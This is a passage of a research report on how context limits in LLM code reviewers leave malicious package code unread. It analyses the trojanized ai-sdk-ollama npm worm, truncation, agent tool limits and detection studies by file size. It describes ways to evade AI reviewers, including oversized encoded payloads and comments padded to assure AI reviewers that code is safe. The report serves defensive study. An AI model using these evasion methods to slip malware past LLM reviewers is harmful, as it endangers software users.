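# Unread code in LLM code review: how context limits hide malicious code, and what batching, sampling and selective reading can do

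## What does a language model see when it reviews code?

In LLM code review, a large language model (LLM), the kind of system behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, reads source code and judges it. This report is concerned with whether the code is malicious, meaning that someone wrote it to steal data, take over machines or do some other harm. Security companies run these systems, called LLM reviewers here, over the public collections from which programmers download ready-made code, often as a last stage after cheaper, rule-based checks. GitHub's advisory database reported 7,197 malware advisories in 2025, 69% more than the year before, according to *CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026), a paper on shortening JavaScript before a model reads it.

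A model can take in only so much text at once, and a reviewer can judge only the code that reaches the model. An attack in June 2026 shows how malicious code could go unread. The JavaScript package ai-sdk-ollama, with over 120,000 downloads a month, lets programmers use locally run language models in their applications. On June 4 an attacker published four malicious versions of it within 17 seconds. In *Trojanized ai-sdk-ollama Delivers Miasma, a Self-Replicating npm Worm via binding.gyp*, Kim and Kennedy (2026) compared one of them, version 3.8.5, with the clean release before it and found the library's build output byte-for-byte identical. The attacker had added two files, a 157-byte build file and 4.5 MB of scrambled JavaScript that steals cloud credentials and spreads itself to other packages. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues, discussing the same package, note that detectors often skip files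 of that size entirely. A reviewer that skipped the larger file would see only a genuine library and a tiny build file, and could declare the package safe without reading the code that does the harm.

Neither source reports that a particular reviewer approved the package. Endor Labs, the security company that published Kim and Kennedy's analysis, identified version 3.8.5 as malicious about 22 minutes after it appeared. The tiny build file was also a clue, since it only launched the large one.

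### Packages and what is in them

A software package is a set of files, published under a name and version number, that other programs can reuse. A registry, such as npm for JavaScript or PyPI for Python, is a public service that stores and distributes packages.

Installing a package copies its files onto a machine, and importing it later loads it into a program. Malicious code can run at either point. Attackers like install scripts, which are commands that run automatically during installation, because they run even if nobody uses the package. *Miasma*, a report from the security company Mend, describes packages under Red Hat's name in which attackers had added an install script to the manifest (the file that lists a package's name, version and scripts). The script ran a 4.1 MB file before any of the package's ordinary code. The attacker behind ai-sdk-ollama declared no install script and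 instead relied on npm automatically starting a build when a package contains a certain kind of build file. Install scripts, build files of this kind and the file that a program loads on import are all entry points, places where a package's code can start running.

In this family of attacks, the payload (the part of a package that does the harm) tends to be one enormous file beside several small ones. Zscaler, another security company, described the same pattern in an earlier wave of attacks from late 2025, with a legitimate-looking loader of about 150 lines and a payload file of more than 480,000 lines.

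Large and unreadable files are not rare in legitimate packages either, so a reviewer can't reject a package just for containing them. Many JavaScript developers use a build tool that merges their program and its third-party libraries into one file, called a bundle. A bundle can be several megabytes, with the author's own code a small fraction of it. Some code is also obfuscated, meaning rewritten so that it does the same thing but is hard to read. Attackers obfuscate code to hide what it does, and some companies do so to protect their intellectual property.

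Coverage is the share of the code, or of the files, that the reviewer has read. These two measures can differ greatly. *Miasma npm Supply Chain Attack* (Likhith, 2026) lists the contents of executable-stories-demo, another package from the June campaign. Its legitimate entry file is 27 KB and its payload is 4.5 MB. A reviewer that skipped only the payload would have read every file but one, yet only about 62 KB of the 4.56 MB for which Likhith gives sizes, or a little over 1%.

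### Tokens and file size

Before a language model processes code, a program called a tokenizer cuts the text into tokens, which may be words, parts of words, punctuation marks or single characters. The context window is the largest number of tokens that a model can take in at once, often between 200,000 and 1,000,000. The code shares this window with the reviewer's instructions, any earlier exchange with the model and anything else in the prompt. Context exhaustion occurs when the code exceeds what the window can hold, so part of it goes unread.

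A file's size is a rough guide to its token count for ordinary code, but not for obfuscated code. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues equate one megabyte with about 250,000 tokens, or four characters per token. Tokenizers learn short representations for character sequences that occur often, so common words take few tokens and random-looking strings take many. "Hello World" takes 2 tokens, while "_0x50e6", a typical name in obfuscated code, is shorter but takes 6.

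Obfuscation can drastically increase the number of tokens in a whole program. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues ran a one-line program that prints "Hello World!" through an off-the-shelf obfuscation tool. The program grew from 6 tokens to 790, about 132 times as many, though it still only prints the greeting. Part of that growth comes from the large amount of text the tool adds. The rest comes from each token covering fewer characters. In the two short strings above, a token covers 5.5 characters in one string and barely more than one character in the other.

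Cloudflare's *Threat report* (2026) shows the same problem in practice. The company, which hosts and protects websites, tested seven models on 100 malicious scripts that its customers had uploaded. The models' input limits ranged from 376 KB to 2.8 MB. The researchers had to cut characters from 47 scripts that were too dense in tokens to fit, and they warn that file size is only a proxy for how much of the context window a script will use.

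Most packages still fit comfortably in a model's context window. *Taint-Style Vulnerability Detection and Confirmation for Node.js Packages Using LLM Agent Reasoning* (Ni, Christodorescu and Jia, 2026) reports that 90% of 17,151 recent npm packages had at most 147,025 tokens in their JavaScript files. *From single pull requests to full software packages*, by Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues at the monitoring company Datadog, reports a median of 5,000 tokens and a 90th percentile of 87,000 for the 10,000 most popular npm packages. The difference in samples may explain the lower figures. The dataset in *Leveraging Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection* (Nguyen, Ho and colleagues, 2025) includes packages of up to 15.8 million tokens.

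So context exhaustion affects a minority of packages. But these distributions mostly describe what honest authors publish, and an attacker can choose the size of a file. The payload in ai-sdk-ollama is an array of 1,338,787 numbers. Even at one token per number, ignoring the commas, it would overflow a million-token window.

### Three forms of reviewer

The simplest LLM reviewer makes one call to a model for each file or package. In the version that Noirot Ferrand and colleagues tested, the model is prompted to rate the maliciousness of a source file from 0 to 1 and state its confidence, and a threshold of 0.5 turns the rating into a verdict. Other reviewers put a whole package into one call. *LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection* (2026) describes one for PyPI packages. It joins all the Python scripts into one text, with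 each file's path in a comment above its contents, and cuts the text off where the context window ends. The files setup.py and \_\_init\_\_.py get priority because they are common entry points for payloads. The main advantage of this design is that the model sees the whole package at once, as long as it fits. If it doesn't fit, the designer has to choose whether the reviewer splits the input, truncates it or skips it.

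A reviewer can split the code into chunks that each fit in the context window, send each chunk to the model separately, and combine the answers by some rule. Nguyen and colleagues built a reviewer of this kind, with chunks of 500 tokens, as a baseline for their own method. The model scores each chunk between 0 and 1, the package takes its highest chunk score, and a package at 0.8 or above counts as malicious. They set the threshold high because a false alarm in one chunk is enough to flag the whole package. In principle this design reads all the code, but it loses the connections between chunks. The lines that collect a password may be in one chunk and the lines that send it away in another, and each chunk may look harmless alone.

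An agent is a model that can use tools and decides, step by step, what to do next. Datadog's system, BewAIre, gives its agent a codemap, which lists the package's files, their sizes, and the locations of functions and other named items, along with a tool for reading a chosen range of lines from a file. Ni and colleagues built an agent that looks for vulnerabilities, which are flaws an attacker could exploit, rather than malware. It searches npm packages for telling patterns and opens the files that seem relevant. An agent can avoid overflowing its context window because it reads only what it requests. But its coverage depends on what it chooses to read, so it may finish without an error and still not have opened the file containing the malicious code.

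Real systems mix these forms. In BewAIre, a cheap model screens everything first, in chunks if the input is large, and passes only what it finds suspicious to the agent. If the cheap model clears a package by mistake, the more capable agent never reviews it.

### The chance of detection

A reviewer's false-negative rate is the share of malicious items that it judges harmless, and its false-positive rate is the share of harmless items that it judges malicious. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues give an example of a false positive in which a model flagged @kittycad/lib, a harmless package, just because the package carries some of its own code as one long encoded string.

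Unread code needs a convention, because a file that the model never received has no verdict. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues count it as judged benign. Their reason is practical: nobody could check by hand all the files that a scanner fails to read across a registry the size of npm. Under this convention a payload that the reviewer never read and a payload that it read and misunderstood both end up in the false-negative rate, which is the number that most evaluations report. The two failures have little else in common, and a simple identity separates them. Let c be the chance that the payload is in the part that the reviewer reads, and d the chance that the reviewer recognises it once it has read it. Then

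chance of detection = c × d

If c is 0.7 and d is 0.9, the chance of detection is 0.63. Out of 1,000 malicious packages, the reviewer reads the payload in 700 and recognises 630 of those. It misses 370 packages, 300 because it never read the payload and 70 because it took the payload for harmless. A model that recognised every payload it read (d = 1) would raise detection only to 0.70, while showing the original model every payload (c = 1) would raise it to 0.90.

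Context exhaustion is a problem of low c. A low d can come from misjudgement, when the model reads a payload but does not understand what it does, or from dilution, when the payload is in the window but the model misses it among a great deal of harmless code. Cloudflare distinguishes payloads in large library bundles that lay outside the window from those that were inside it but still went unnoticed. Nguyen and colleagues likewise argue that harmless code acts as noise even when the window is long enough to hold it.

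The identity is exact only if a reviewer never flags a package whose payload it has not read. This is true by definition when each file gets its own verdict and unread files count as benign. It is not always true when one verdict covers a whole package. A reviewer might have flagged ai-sdk-ollama after reading only the 157-byte build file, and in such cases c × d understates the chance of detection.

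A more common mistake would be to use coverage in place of c. The two are equal if the payload is equally likely to be anywhere in the code, but attackers do not place payloads at random. The reviewer that skips one file in executable-stories-demo covers nearly all the files, but its c for that package is zero.

Raising c can lower d. Putting more code into a single call makes the call more likely to include the payload, but it also surrounds the payload with more harmless code. Small chunks remove much of that surrounding code but may split the payload into pieces that mean little on their own, so d can fall even when c is 1.

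## How does part of a codebase go unread?

Code can drop out of a review before the model receives any input, or much later, when an agent's context window has filled up. How much this matters depends partly on whether the model or the operator finds out. A model that is notified of missing code can request the rest, and an operator who sees a skipped file in a log can have a person review it. If neither finds out, the review looks complete even though some code went unread.

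### Files over a size limit

Some scanners check a file's size before calling the model and skip the file if it is too large. Doutre and colleagues mention in passing that Datadog's pipeline for collecting new npm and PyPI releases also enforces size limits, so a large enough package might not reach a model at all. Ordinary code makes this decision, so the model receives no information about the skipped file. The operator finds out only if the scanner logs the skip, and what the user sees depends on how the system counts a file without a verdict.

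The payload file in ai-sdk-ollama shows why a scanner would do this. Nearly all of its 4.5 MB is the array of 1,338,787 integers, each of which stands for one character of hidden text. When the file runs, a short function turns the integers back into text, and JavaScript's eval command runs that text as a program. If each number and each comma takes one token, the array comes to about 2.7 million tokens, nearly three times what a million-token window can hold. (The rule of thumb for ordinary code would put the file at only 1.1 million.)

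A scanner could split the file instead. With a 200,000-token window, that would take at least 14 calls, nearly all containing only numbers. Price is a weaker reason to skip the file. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues list a price of $0.20 per million input tokens for GPT-5.6 Luna, one of the models they tested. At that rate, reading the array once would cost about 54 cents. That is little for one file, but it is about 20 times what Doutre and colleagues estimate for a median npm package, and some providers charge more per token for very long prompts.

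Reading every number in the array would not reveal what the program does. Kim and Kennedy decoded the array and found two more programs inside, both encrypted, the larger about 668 KB. But a reviewer could become suspicious without seeing the hidden programs, because the decoding function and the eval command are readable at the top of the file. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues expect a scanner to judge the file malicious from this visible obfuscation alone, once something has shortened the array. A scanner that skips the file misses those lines as well as the numbers.

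### Input cut to fit the window

Truncation keeps part of the input and discards the rest. It happens when the code and instructions together exceed the context window or a smaller limit set by a developer. The model provider rejects a request that no longer fits, according to *Managing Context & Compaction*, Docker's guide to its own agent, so the software around the model usually has to do the cutting.

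Whether the model can detect that something is missing depends on how the software makes the cut. Docker's agent has an optional cap on tool results, the text that a tool such as a file reader returns to the model. If a result is too long, the agent keeps the beginning and end and replaces the middle with a marker, so the model can detect the gap. Docker says the beginning and end are usually the most informative parts. That may be true of a build log, but there is no reason to expect it of source code that an attacker has written.

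Truncation can cut off the reviewer's instructions as well as the code. According to GitHub (2026), Copilot code review, which comments on proposed changes to a repository, read only the first 4,000 characters of a team's custom instruction files until GitHub removed the limit in June. If a team had written "check every install script" past that limit, Copilot would not have received the rule.

When a scanner joins a whole package into one text and then cuts it, the order of the files determines which ones are removed. The PyPI reviewer therefore gives priority to common entry points.

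### Files that a product leaves out

Some products skip files because of their name, type or location, whatever their size. According to a copy of GitHub's documentation hosted on another site, Copilot code review excludes dependency management files, log files, SVG images, and files in places that usually hold third-party or automatically generated code. The excluded files include package-lock.json and yarn.lock, which record the exact versions of a project's dependencies, and jest.config.js and next.config.js, which configure a testing tool and a web framework. A companion page in the same copy also lists package.json, the manifest of an npm package.

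These exclusions suit a tool that looks for programming mistakes, since few developers want comments on thousands of lines of version numbers, but they are a poor fit for finding malicious code. The malicious install script in the Red Hat packages, for example, was in package.json. A file like jest.config.js is an ordinary JavaScript program that runs whenever someone runs the tests. Kim and Kennedy also found that the June worm writes settings files into its victims' repositories that start the payload when a developer opens the project in certain editors or coding agents. A team that relies on Copilot code review therefore needs some other check on its manifests, configuration files and third-party code.

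Since June 2026, GitHub has also let administrators exclude chosen paths from Copilot code review, either to protect sensitive material or to remove irrelevant context. In September, GitHub announced in *Content exclusions generally available in Copilot app and CLI* (2026) that the Copilot app and command-line tool now respect such policies too. According to GitHub's documentation, the edit and agent modes of Copilot Chat do not support them, so what Copilot reads in a repository depends on which Copilot product someone is using.

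GitHub publishes its own rules, and administrators know the ones they wrote. But a developer who sees no comments on a file can't tell from that alone whether Copilot found nothing wrong or never read it.

Code can also go unread because a tool doesn't support the language it is written in. The preprocessor that Noirot Ferrand and colleagues built handles only JavaScript, and they state that it does not cover malicious behaviour found entirely in compiled binaries.

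### Files that an agent does not open

An agent reads only the files it requests, so two runs over the same repository can cover different code. Mercury's *Beyond agentic security scanning* (2026) describes this problem at a financial technology company that used agents to search its own code for authorization flaws, which let one user reach another user's data. One run might read a helper function that another missed, and a third might collect different surrounding code. When the results changed, the engineers could not tell whether a new prompt had helped or the agent had just read different files. They warn that an agent that reads the wrong code or stops too early can still write a confident report.

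Mercury gives no count of how often this happened, and its post argues for an alternative that the company built. In its example, the agent raises a false alarm because it stops before reaching the check that makes the code safe. In a search for malware, stopping early would more likely make the agent miss it, because the unread file could be the payload. Mercury points out that using one agent to gather code and another to judge it does not solve the problem, because the second agent depends on what the first selected.

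The ai-sdk-ollama manifest lists the clean library file as the package's entry point. Likhith notes that in a sister package with the same layout, application code never imports the payload file. An agent that started at the manifest and followed the imports could finish without opening the payload, unless it also looked at the 157-byte build file.

Even a reviewer that opens the right file may miss part of it, because file-reading tools limit how much they return. The file reader from LangChain, a company that makes software for building agents, returns up to 100 lines from the start of a file by default, according to its *READ_FILE_TOOL_DESCRIPTION*. The description, which is written for the model, recommends reading large files in sections and reading a file in full only when that is necessary for editing. A reviewer doesn't edit, so this amounts to advice never to read a whole file. One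 default call on the payload of more than 480,000 lines from late 2025 would return about 0.02% of the file.

Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, is more explicit about what is missing. According to Anthropic's *Tools reference*, if a file exceeds the token limit for one read, the tool returns the first page with a "PARTIAL view" notice stating how much the model has received and how to read more. A partial read does not count as reading the file when Claude Code checks whether the model may edit it. This rule covers edits, so a model can still give an opinion on a file after seeing one page.

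Other tools in Claude Code have their own limits:

- A search by file name returns at most 100 files, sorted by modification time, with a flag if there were more.
- A search of file contents skips files that the project's .gitignore lists, which are typically build output and downloaded dependencies. The search by file name does find them, and the model can search one by giving its path.
- A successful shell command returns up to roughly 30,000 characters directly. Beyond that the model gets a short preview and the path of a saved copy. An agent that printed the ai-sdk-ollama payload this way would see only its first lines unless it went on to read the copy.

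The model can react to a flag or a preview, but not to a tool failure that is reported as an ordinary result. Before version 2.1.208, Claude Code's content search returned "No files found" when it rejected a search pattern as invalid, even if the text was in the files. An agent looking for a suspicious command could have concluded that the command was absent. The search now returns an error instead.

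### Material lost during a long session

The code an agent reads stays in its context window, along with file lists, search results and its own earlier messages. As the window fills, the software running the agent has to make room.

One way code can go unread is through compaction, which replaces messages with a summary of them, as Anthropic's *Compaction overview* describes. By default, Docker's agent compacts its session once it estimates that usage has passed 90% of the context window. Claude Code also compacts automatically near the limit. After compaction in Claude Code, Anthropic notes, a file of more than 5,000 tokens comes back as a path without its contents.

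A summary reads like a complete account, so the model may not know that anything is missing. It also reflects what seemed important when it was written. A summary might not mention a function that reads a machine's settings, because the function looks routine on its own. It looks suspicious once the model finds code in another file that sends those settings to an unknown server, but by then the function may no longer be in the context window.

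The summary may not draw on the whole session. OpenClaw, an open-source agent, usually writes it with a single request. According to OpenClaw's documentation, each request can include at most 160,000 characters of conversation text, or about 40,000 tokens. If the older part of a session is 200,000 tokens long, a single request can include at most about a fifth of it.

The other method is to delete old tool results and keep the rest of the conversation. Anthropic's *Context editing* describes a version that deletes the oldest results first once the conversation passes a set size, and leaves placeholder text so the model can see that something was removed. In a separate guide, Anthropic points out that the record of the call remains and that the agent can fetch the material again. That makes deletion easier to recover from than a bad summary. But it can mislead anyone who works out coverage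 from the record of calls, because a file the agent opened earlier counts as read even if its contents were no longer in the window when the model gave its verdict.

### Calls that fail

A request that exceeds the context window may fail, and the designer has to decide what happens then. In Docker's account, the session stalls, which a user will at least notice. Doutre and colleagues report that when a flagged package was too large for the investigating agent, Datadog's reviewer at one stage fell back on the verdict of the cheaper model that had screened the package first. The caller still received a verdict, but the deeper investigation had not taken place.

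In that system the fallback probably did limited harm to detection. The agent receives only flagged packages, so falling back should leave a package flagged and cause some false alarms. The same design would be dangerous in a system that sends every package to both models, because the weaker model's verdict could clear a package that the stronger model never read. Retrying with less code would avoid the fallback, but the system would again have to choose what to leave out. The payload can also go unread because a model refuses to continue before reaching it.

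### Accidental size and deliberate padding

Most oversized code has an innocent explanation. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues looked for separable parts, such as bundled modules, in 512 large npm files and found them in 244. Those files had a mean of 83 modules and a median of one, and the largest bundle had 2,840. Dependency upgrades are another common cause. Doutre and colleagues first ran into context limits while reviewing proposed changes to Datadog's own code, and the changes that upgraded dependencies were especially large.

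The same npm dataset suggests that file size is a poor sign of malice. Of its 2,442 malicious files, 166 (7%) have more than 25,000 tokens, compared with 346 (14%) of its 2,442 harmless files. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues removed duplicates from the same attack campaign, so a campaign that published hundreds of copies of one huge file has little effect on these figures. Even so, because harmless packages vastly outnumber malicious ones on npm, a scanner that flagged every large file would mostly flag harmless code.

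Attackers can also deliberately enlarge a file with material that doesn't change what the program does, either to push the payload out of the context window or to hide it among harmless code. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues design for an attacker who does this and write that real attackers already exploit limited context windows.

For ai-sdk-ollama the motive is less clear. Writing each character as a number more than triples the length of the hidden text, but it also hides the text from simple searches, which may have been its only purpose. Kim and Kennedy found that the attacker had changed the encoding between versions published within the same minute, which they interpret as an attempt to evade scanners that look for fixed patterns. They don't suggest that the attacker chose the file's size with a language model in mind, and the file may have overflowed the context window by accident.

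## How much malicious code is missed in large files?

Few researchers have measured how detection varies with file size, but their results show that LLM reviewers miss far more malicious code in large files than in small ones. The cause is harder to establish, because most published miss rates don't separate payloads the model never read from those it read but judged harmless.

### Cloudflare's results by file size

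The steepest drop comes from the test Cloudflare published in April 2026, which used 100 customer scripts. In March, Cloudforce One, the company's threat research team, had found scripts padded with thousands of lines of comments assuring AI reviewers that the code was safe, and it designed the test to find out whether such comments work. It ran seven models on 23 versions of each script, 18,400 calls in all, and gave each model as much of the script as its context window allowed. File size affected the results more than the comments did. The rates below pool all the models' verdicts on the original scripts, without added comments.

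| Script size | Scripts | Judged malicious |
|---|---|---|
| Under 100 KB | 36 | 94.1% |
| 100–500 KB | 18 | 100% |
| 500 KB–1 MB | 3 | 70.8% |
| 1–3 MB | 10 | 70.0% |
| Over 3 MB | 33 | 17.6% |

Detection was high below 500 KB and very low above 3 MB, and chance is unlikely to explain so large a difference. The rates between those sizes are much less certain. With only ten scripts, a rate of 70% is compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 40% to 90%, and a rate based on three scripts is almost uninformative. We therefore can't tell from the table at what size detection collapses.

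The number of calls is also odd. Judging 23 versions of 100 scripts would take 16,100 calls with the seven models listed, but 18,400, the number reported, with eight. The 70.8% in the table is 17 out of 24 verdicts, and 24 is eight verdicts on each of three scripts. Perhaps one model ran twice, or the team left one out of its list. This hardly affects the pattern, but the pooled rates probably include a set of verdicts that Cloudflare doesn't describe.

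A more serious worry is that large and small scripts may do different things. Phishing made up 52% of the collection and proxies, which relay a user's internet traffic, another 35%. The rest hosted files or abused streaming services. Cloudflare confirmed the scripts through its own blocking rules, so some may break its terms without being malware in the ordinary sense. A model could read every line of a proxy and reasonably call it harmless. If proxies were common among the largest scripts, detection would be lower for those scripts even if size itself had no effect. Cloudflare does not break down the types by size. At least some of the large scripts were plainly malicious, though. The report mentions code that sends stolen data to the messaging service Telegram, buried in thousands of lines of library code.

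### Truncation or dilution?

Cloudflare blames both context exhaustion and dilution. The first can be checked with some arithmetic. Suppose the software keeps the first part of a file and the payload is equally likely to be anywhere in it. Then c, the chance that the payload reaches the model, is the size of the window divided by the size of the file. For the smallest and largest windows in the test, and for files of 3 MB and 6.3 MB (the largest in the collection), that gives:

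| Window | 3 MB file | 6.3 MB file |
|---|---|---|
| 376 KB | 12.5% | 6% |
| 2.8 MB | 93% | 44% |

If the model with the 2.8 MB window had recognised every payload it received, it would have caught between 44% and 93% of the scripts above 3 MB. Truncation alone therefore can't explain a detection rate near 18%.

Truncation alone could explain the pooled rate of 17.6%. If all the other models had context windows close to 376 KB, truncation would produce an average between about 11% and 24%. Cloudflare does not publish the other models' window sizes or each model's results by size.

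The paper reports the share of original scripts that each model flagged, and the results are the opposite of what we would expect if truncation explained the differences between models. The model with the smallest context window flagged 90% of the scripts, more than any other, while the model with the largest flagged 62%.

The overall rates also limit how many scripts above 3 MB each model can have flagged. Only 67 of the 100 scripts were smaller than that, so a model that flagged 90 must have flagged at least 23 of the 33 large ones, or about 70%, even though its window could hold no more than an eighth of each. The other models can therefore have averaged roughly 10% at most on the large scripts. The model with the 2.8 MB window may have flagged almost none of them. It flagged 62 scripts in total, and at the pooled rates a model would flag about 61 of the 67 smaller ones. It could have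 done worse than average on small scripts and better on large ones, but the published figures give no evidence of this.

Payloads may not be randomly placed. In a short example bundle from Noirot Ferrand and colleagues, the bundle author's own code comes after the library modules. If many of the large scripts had that layout and the software cut off the end, even a model with a 2.8 MB window could have failed to receive the payload in a 3 MB file. But then the model with the 376 KB window should not have received it either, and that model did best.

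Two explanations remain for its success. One is that the small window removed most of the harmless code around the payload, which would be evidence of dilution in the other models. This requires the short extract to have included the payload, and Cloudflare doesn't say how it cut the text. The other is that this model could be calling nearly everything malicious. The team tested no harmless scripts, so there is no false-positive rate to rule this out.

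### Large files on npm

Noirot Ferrand and colleagues tested both malicious and harmless files. As a baseline for their preprocessor, they ran their single-call reviewer and a three-stage reviewer on the unprocessed code of all 4,884 npm files published between January 2025 and July 2026 in their dataset. The three-stage reviewer, based on a commercial scanner called SocketAI, has the model write a report, criticise it and then produce a final version. The researchers looked separately at the 512 files above 25,000 tokens, of which 166 were malicious.

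The next table shows coverage on those large files, followed by false-negative rates. The last column is calculated from the published rates, with the large files left out of the total.

| Reviewer | Coverage, large files | Missed, large files | Missed, all files | Missed, smaller files |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Single call, GPT-5 nano | 69.5% | 36.7% | 7.2% | 5% |
| Single call, GPT-5.6 Luna | 69.7% | 34.9% | 7.3% | 5% |
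| Single call, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 69.7% | 34.3% | 11.5% | 10% |
| Three stages, GPT-5 nano | 69.1% | 30.1% | 10.5% | 9% |
| Three stages, GPT-5.6 Luna | 85.7% | 28.3% | 9.5% | 8% |
| Three stages, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 69.1% | 40.4% | 10.6% | 8% |

Coverage of all 4,884 files was between 96.7% and 98.5%. Large files made up 7% of the malicious ones but accounted for between a fifth and a third of everything the reviewers missed.

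A file of 25,000 tokens fits easily in a current context window, so most of the "large" files fit too. In five of the six set-ups, about 156 files went unread, which is close to the number of files in the collection above 250,000 tokens, or roughly 1 MB (about 160). The reviewers therefore probably failed on nearly every file above that size and read nearly everything below it.

The coverage figures combine malicious and harmless files, so we can't tell from them how many of the missed payloads were in unread files. We can make a rough estimate by assuming that malicious files went unread as often as harmless ones. In the first row of the table, the reviewer missed 61 malicious files. Under this assumption, about 51 of those were unread, and the reviewer misjudged about 10 of the 115 it read. Its chance of recognising a payload it had read, d, would then be about 0.91, compared with 0.95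 for smaller files, so nearly all the extra loss would come from unread code. Cloudflare's results, by contrast, suggest that the models with large windows received many payloads and failed to recognise them.

Counting unread files as benign also artificially lowers the false-positive rate, which was between 0% and 1.2% on the large files, because a reviewer can't raise a false alarm about a harmless file it never reads.

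All four authors are affiliated with Socket, which sells a scanner of this kind. Socket also funded the work, and its staff labelled the packages. A weak baseline makes the paper's proposed remedy look better, and this baseline leaves oversized files unread where another scanner might split them. However, Noirot Ferrand and colleagues openly call the three-stage design a leftover from the days of weaker models, and they report that a single call does nearly as well for 12% to 31% of the cost.

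The test was easier than real scanning in one respect, because each malicious item was a file already known to contain the payload, so the reviewer never had to find the right file in a package. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, rebuilt the SocketAI workflow from its published description and ran it on whole packages with an older model, GPT-4.1 mini. The rebuilt workflow missed 3,569 of 6,420 malicious packages, or 56%. Unread code explains only some of these misses. The workflow read at most 20 files per package, which left payloads in deep directories unread, but its second stage also led the model to reverse correct verdicts, and the model scored some malware below the threshold. Another tool, which used the same model and compared pieces of each package with known malware, missed only 6%.

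### Separating the two kinds of miss

*MalTotal* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) more cleanly separates the malicious projects that did not fit in the model's context from those the model read and classified as harmless. The researchers collected 250 malicious projects, 50 in each of five programming languages, chosen to span five size tiers. They joined each project's code into one text and sent it to DeepSeek-V3.

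Of the 250 projects, 63 were too long for the model to read. The rates for each language imply that it missed 9 of the 187 that fit, or 4.8%, slightly above the 4.1% in the paper's summary row. In the identity given earlier, c is 0.748 and d is 0.952, so the chance of detection is 0.71. If the 63 unread projects count as benign, the false-negative rate is 29%, and seven-eighths of the misses are projects the model never received.

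JavaScript was the exception. Seven of its 50 projects did not fit, and the model missed another seven of the 43 that did. Zhao and colleagues then sent only the files containing sensitive operations, such as running a command or opening a network connection. Two projects still did not fit, and the model again missed seven. When they extracted the malicious logic by hand and sent only that, the model missed one of 50.

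The model could therefore recognise almost all of this code when it was shown alone, so dilution probably caused most of the misses among projects that fit in the context window. But this evidence comes from only seven projects, and the people who prepared the extracts already knew where the malicious code was. The experiment also included no harmless projects, so a model biased towards flagging code as malicious would have scored well.

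Cloudflare's data don't settle whether large malicious packages are simply harder to recognise. *LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection* helps answer this by comparing packages with at most 1.57 KB of Python code with packages of at least 700 KB. Qwen3-14b detected 92% of the malicious packages in the smaller group and 35% in the larger one. For DeepSeek-R1-70b, the share fell from 98% to 17%.

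HERCULE is a tool that runs a package in isolation and monitors what it does. Its detection rate fell much less with package size, from 94% for the smallest malicious packages to 91% for the largest. A method that didn't depend on reading all the code could therefore still find the evidence of malice in large packages.

The researchers attribute the models' decline to truncation, even though they prioritized common entry points when cutting. Much of the decline occurs well below 700 KB. Their figures for packages above 5 KB, excluding the very large ones, imply detection rates of about 60% for Qwen3-14b and 46% for DeepSeek-R1-70b. These rates combine packages that fit in the context window with packages that didn't, so they don't isolate dilution. Both models are also open and small by current standards, and a stronger model with a larger window might start to fail at a different size.

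On the largest packages, DeepSeek-R1-70b did worse than random guessing. Its published precision implies that it flagged about 36% of the harmless packages, twice its rate for the malicious ones.

### Benchmarks made of small packages

Many evaluations contain too few large files to reveal a problem with them. Ryan, Khalil and colleagues (2026), in *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages*, tested 13 models, four of which scored perfectly on detection in at least one configuration. Half of their malicious packages had 36 lines of code or fewer. The harmless packages they started with had a median of 288 lines and a mean of 134,148, because a few were enormous. They kept only the smallest ones, up to 260 lines, partly so that everything would fit in the models' context windows.

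Even there, the models were somewhat less accurate on longer packages when asked to name the specific signs of malice in each one (a rank correlation of −0.26, where −1 would be a perfect decline). Packages of a few dozen lines fit easily in any context window. Ryan and colleagues point out that longer packages contain more such signs, which gives a model more to get wrong, so this is weak evidence of dilution.

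Vulnerability research has a similar gap. Ni and colleagues found that 90% of the packages in two widely used collections had at most 32,448 tokens, while 90% of recently published npm packages had at most 147,025.

Malware collections have a further bias because they contain only what somebody has already caught. If scanners tend to miss large payloads, those payloads are also less likely to appear in the datasets researchers use to measure miss rates.

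## Would a larger context window solve the problem?

Context windows have grown quickly. CodeBERT, an early language model for code, could process 512 to 1,024 tokens, according to Nguyen and colleagues. By 2024, the open model Llama 3 70B had a window of 8,000 tokens, and OpenAI's GPT-4o had one of 128,000. Llama 3.3, which is the same size as Llama 3 70B, has a window of 128,000 tokens, and GPT-4.1 has one of 1,000,000. In September 2026, Noirot Ferrand and colleagues put the usual range at 200,000 to 1,000,000 tokens.

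According to Ni and colleagues, at least 90% of recent npm packages already fit whole in a window of 200,000 tokens. Expanding the window to a million tokens therefore makes a difference only for the few very large packages, which are the ones where code goes unread.

### How much detection could rise

The benefit of a larger window depends on what the reviewer used to do with code that didn't fit. If it skipped such code and counted it as benign, a larger window can only raise detection, because the model still receives small packages exactly as before and may now recognise payloads in code it previously couldn't read. There will also be some extra false alarms, because the model now judges large harmless files too.

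A larger window can also do harm if the reviewer previously truncated the code. If the truncated text included the payload, c was already 1 for that package, so the larger window cannot raise it, and the extra harmless code may lower d.

In the experiment by Zhao and colleagues, 63 of 250 malicious projects did not fit in the context window, and overall detection was 71%. Suppose a larger window held all 63. If the model detected them as often as it detected the rest, overall detection would rise to 95%. If it detected only 17.6% of them, the pooled rate for scripts above 3 MB in Cloudflare's test, overall detection would rise to just 76%. Cloudflare's figure includes some truncation, so it is probably too pessimistic. The gain could still range from 5 to 24 points, depending on how well models recognise a payload in a very long input.

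One comparison in the results of Noirot Ferrand and colleagues suggests a figure between these extremes. With GPT-5.6 Luna, their single-call reviewer read 69.7% of the large files and their three-stage reviewer read 85.7%, or about 82 more files. If malicious files were as common among those 82 as among all the large files, about 27 of them were malicious. But the three-stage reviewer missed 47 malicious files instead of 58, a reduction of only 11, which would mean the model recognised under half of the additional payloads it received. The comparison is rough because the three-stage design also did slightly worse on small files, so the design itself may account for some of the shortfall.

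### Code that fits in no window

The largest package in Nguyen and colleagues' dataset has 15.8 million tokens. It would fill a million-token window almost 16 times and a 200,000-token window 79 times.

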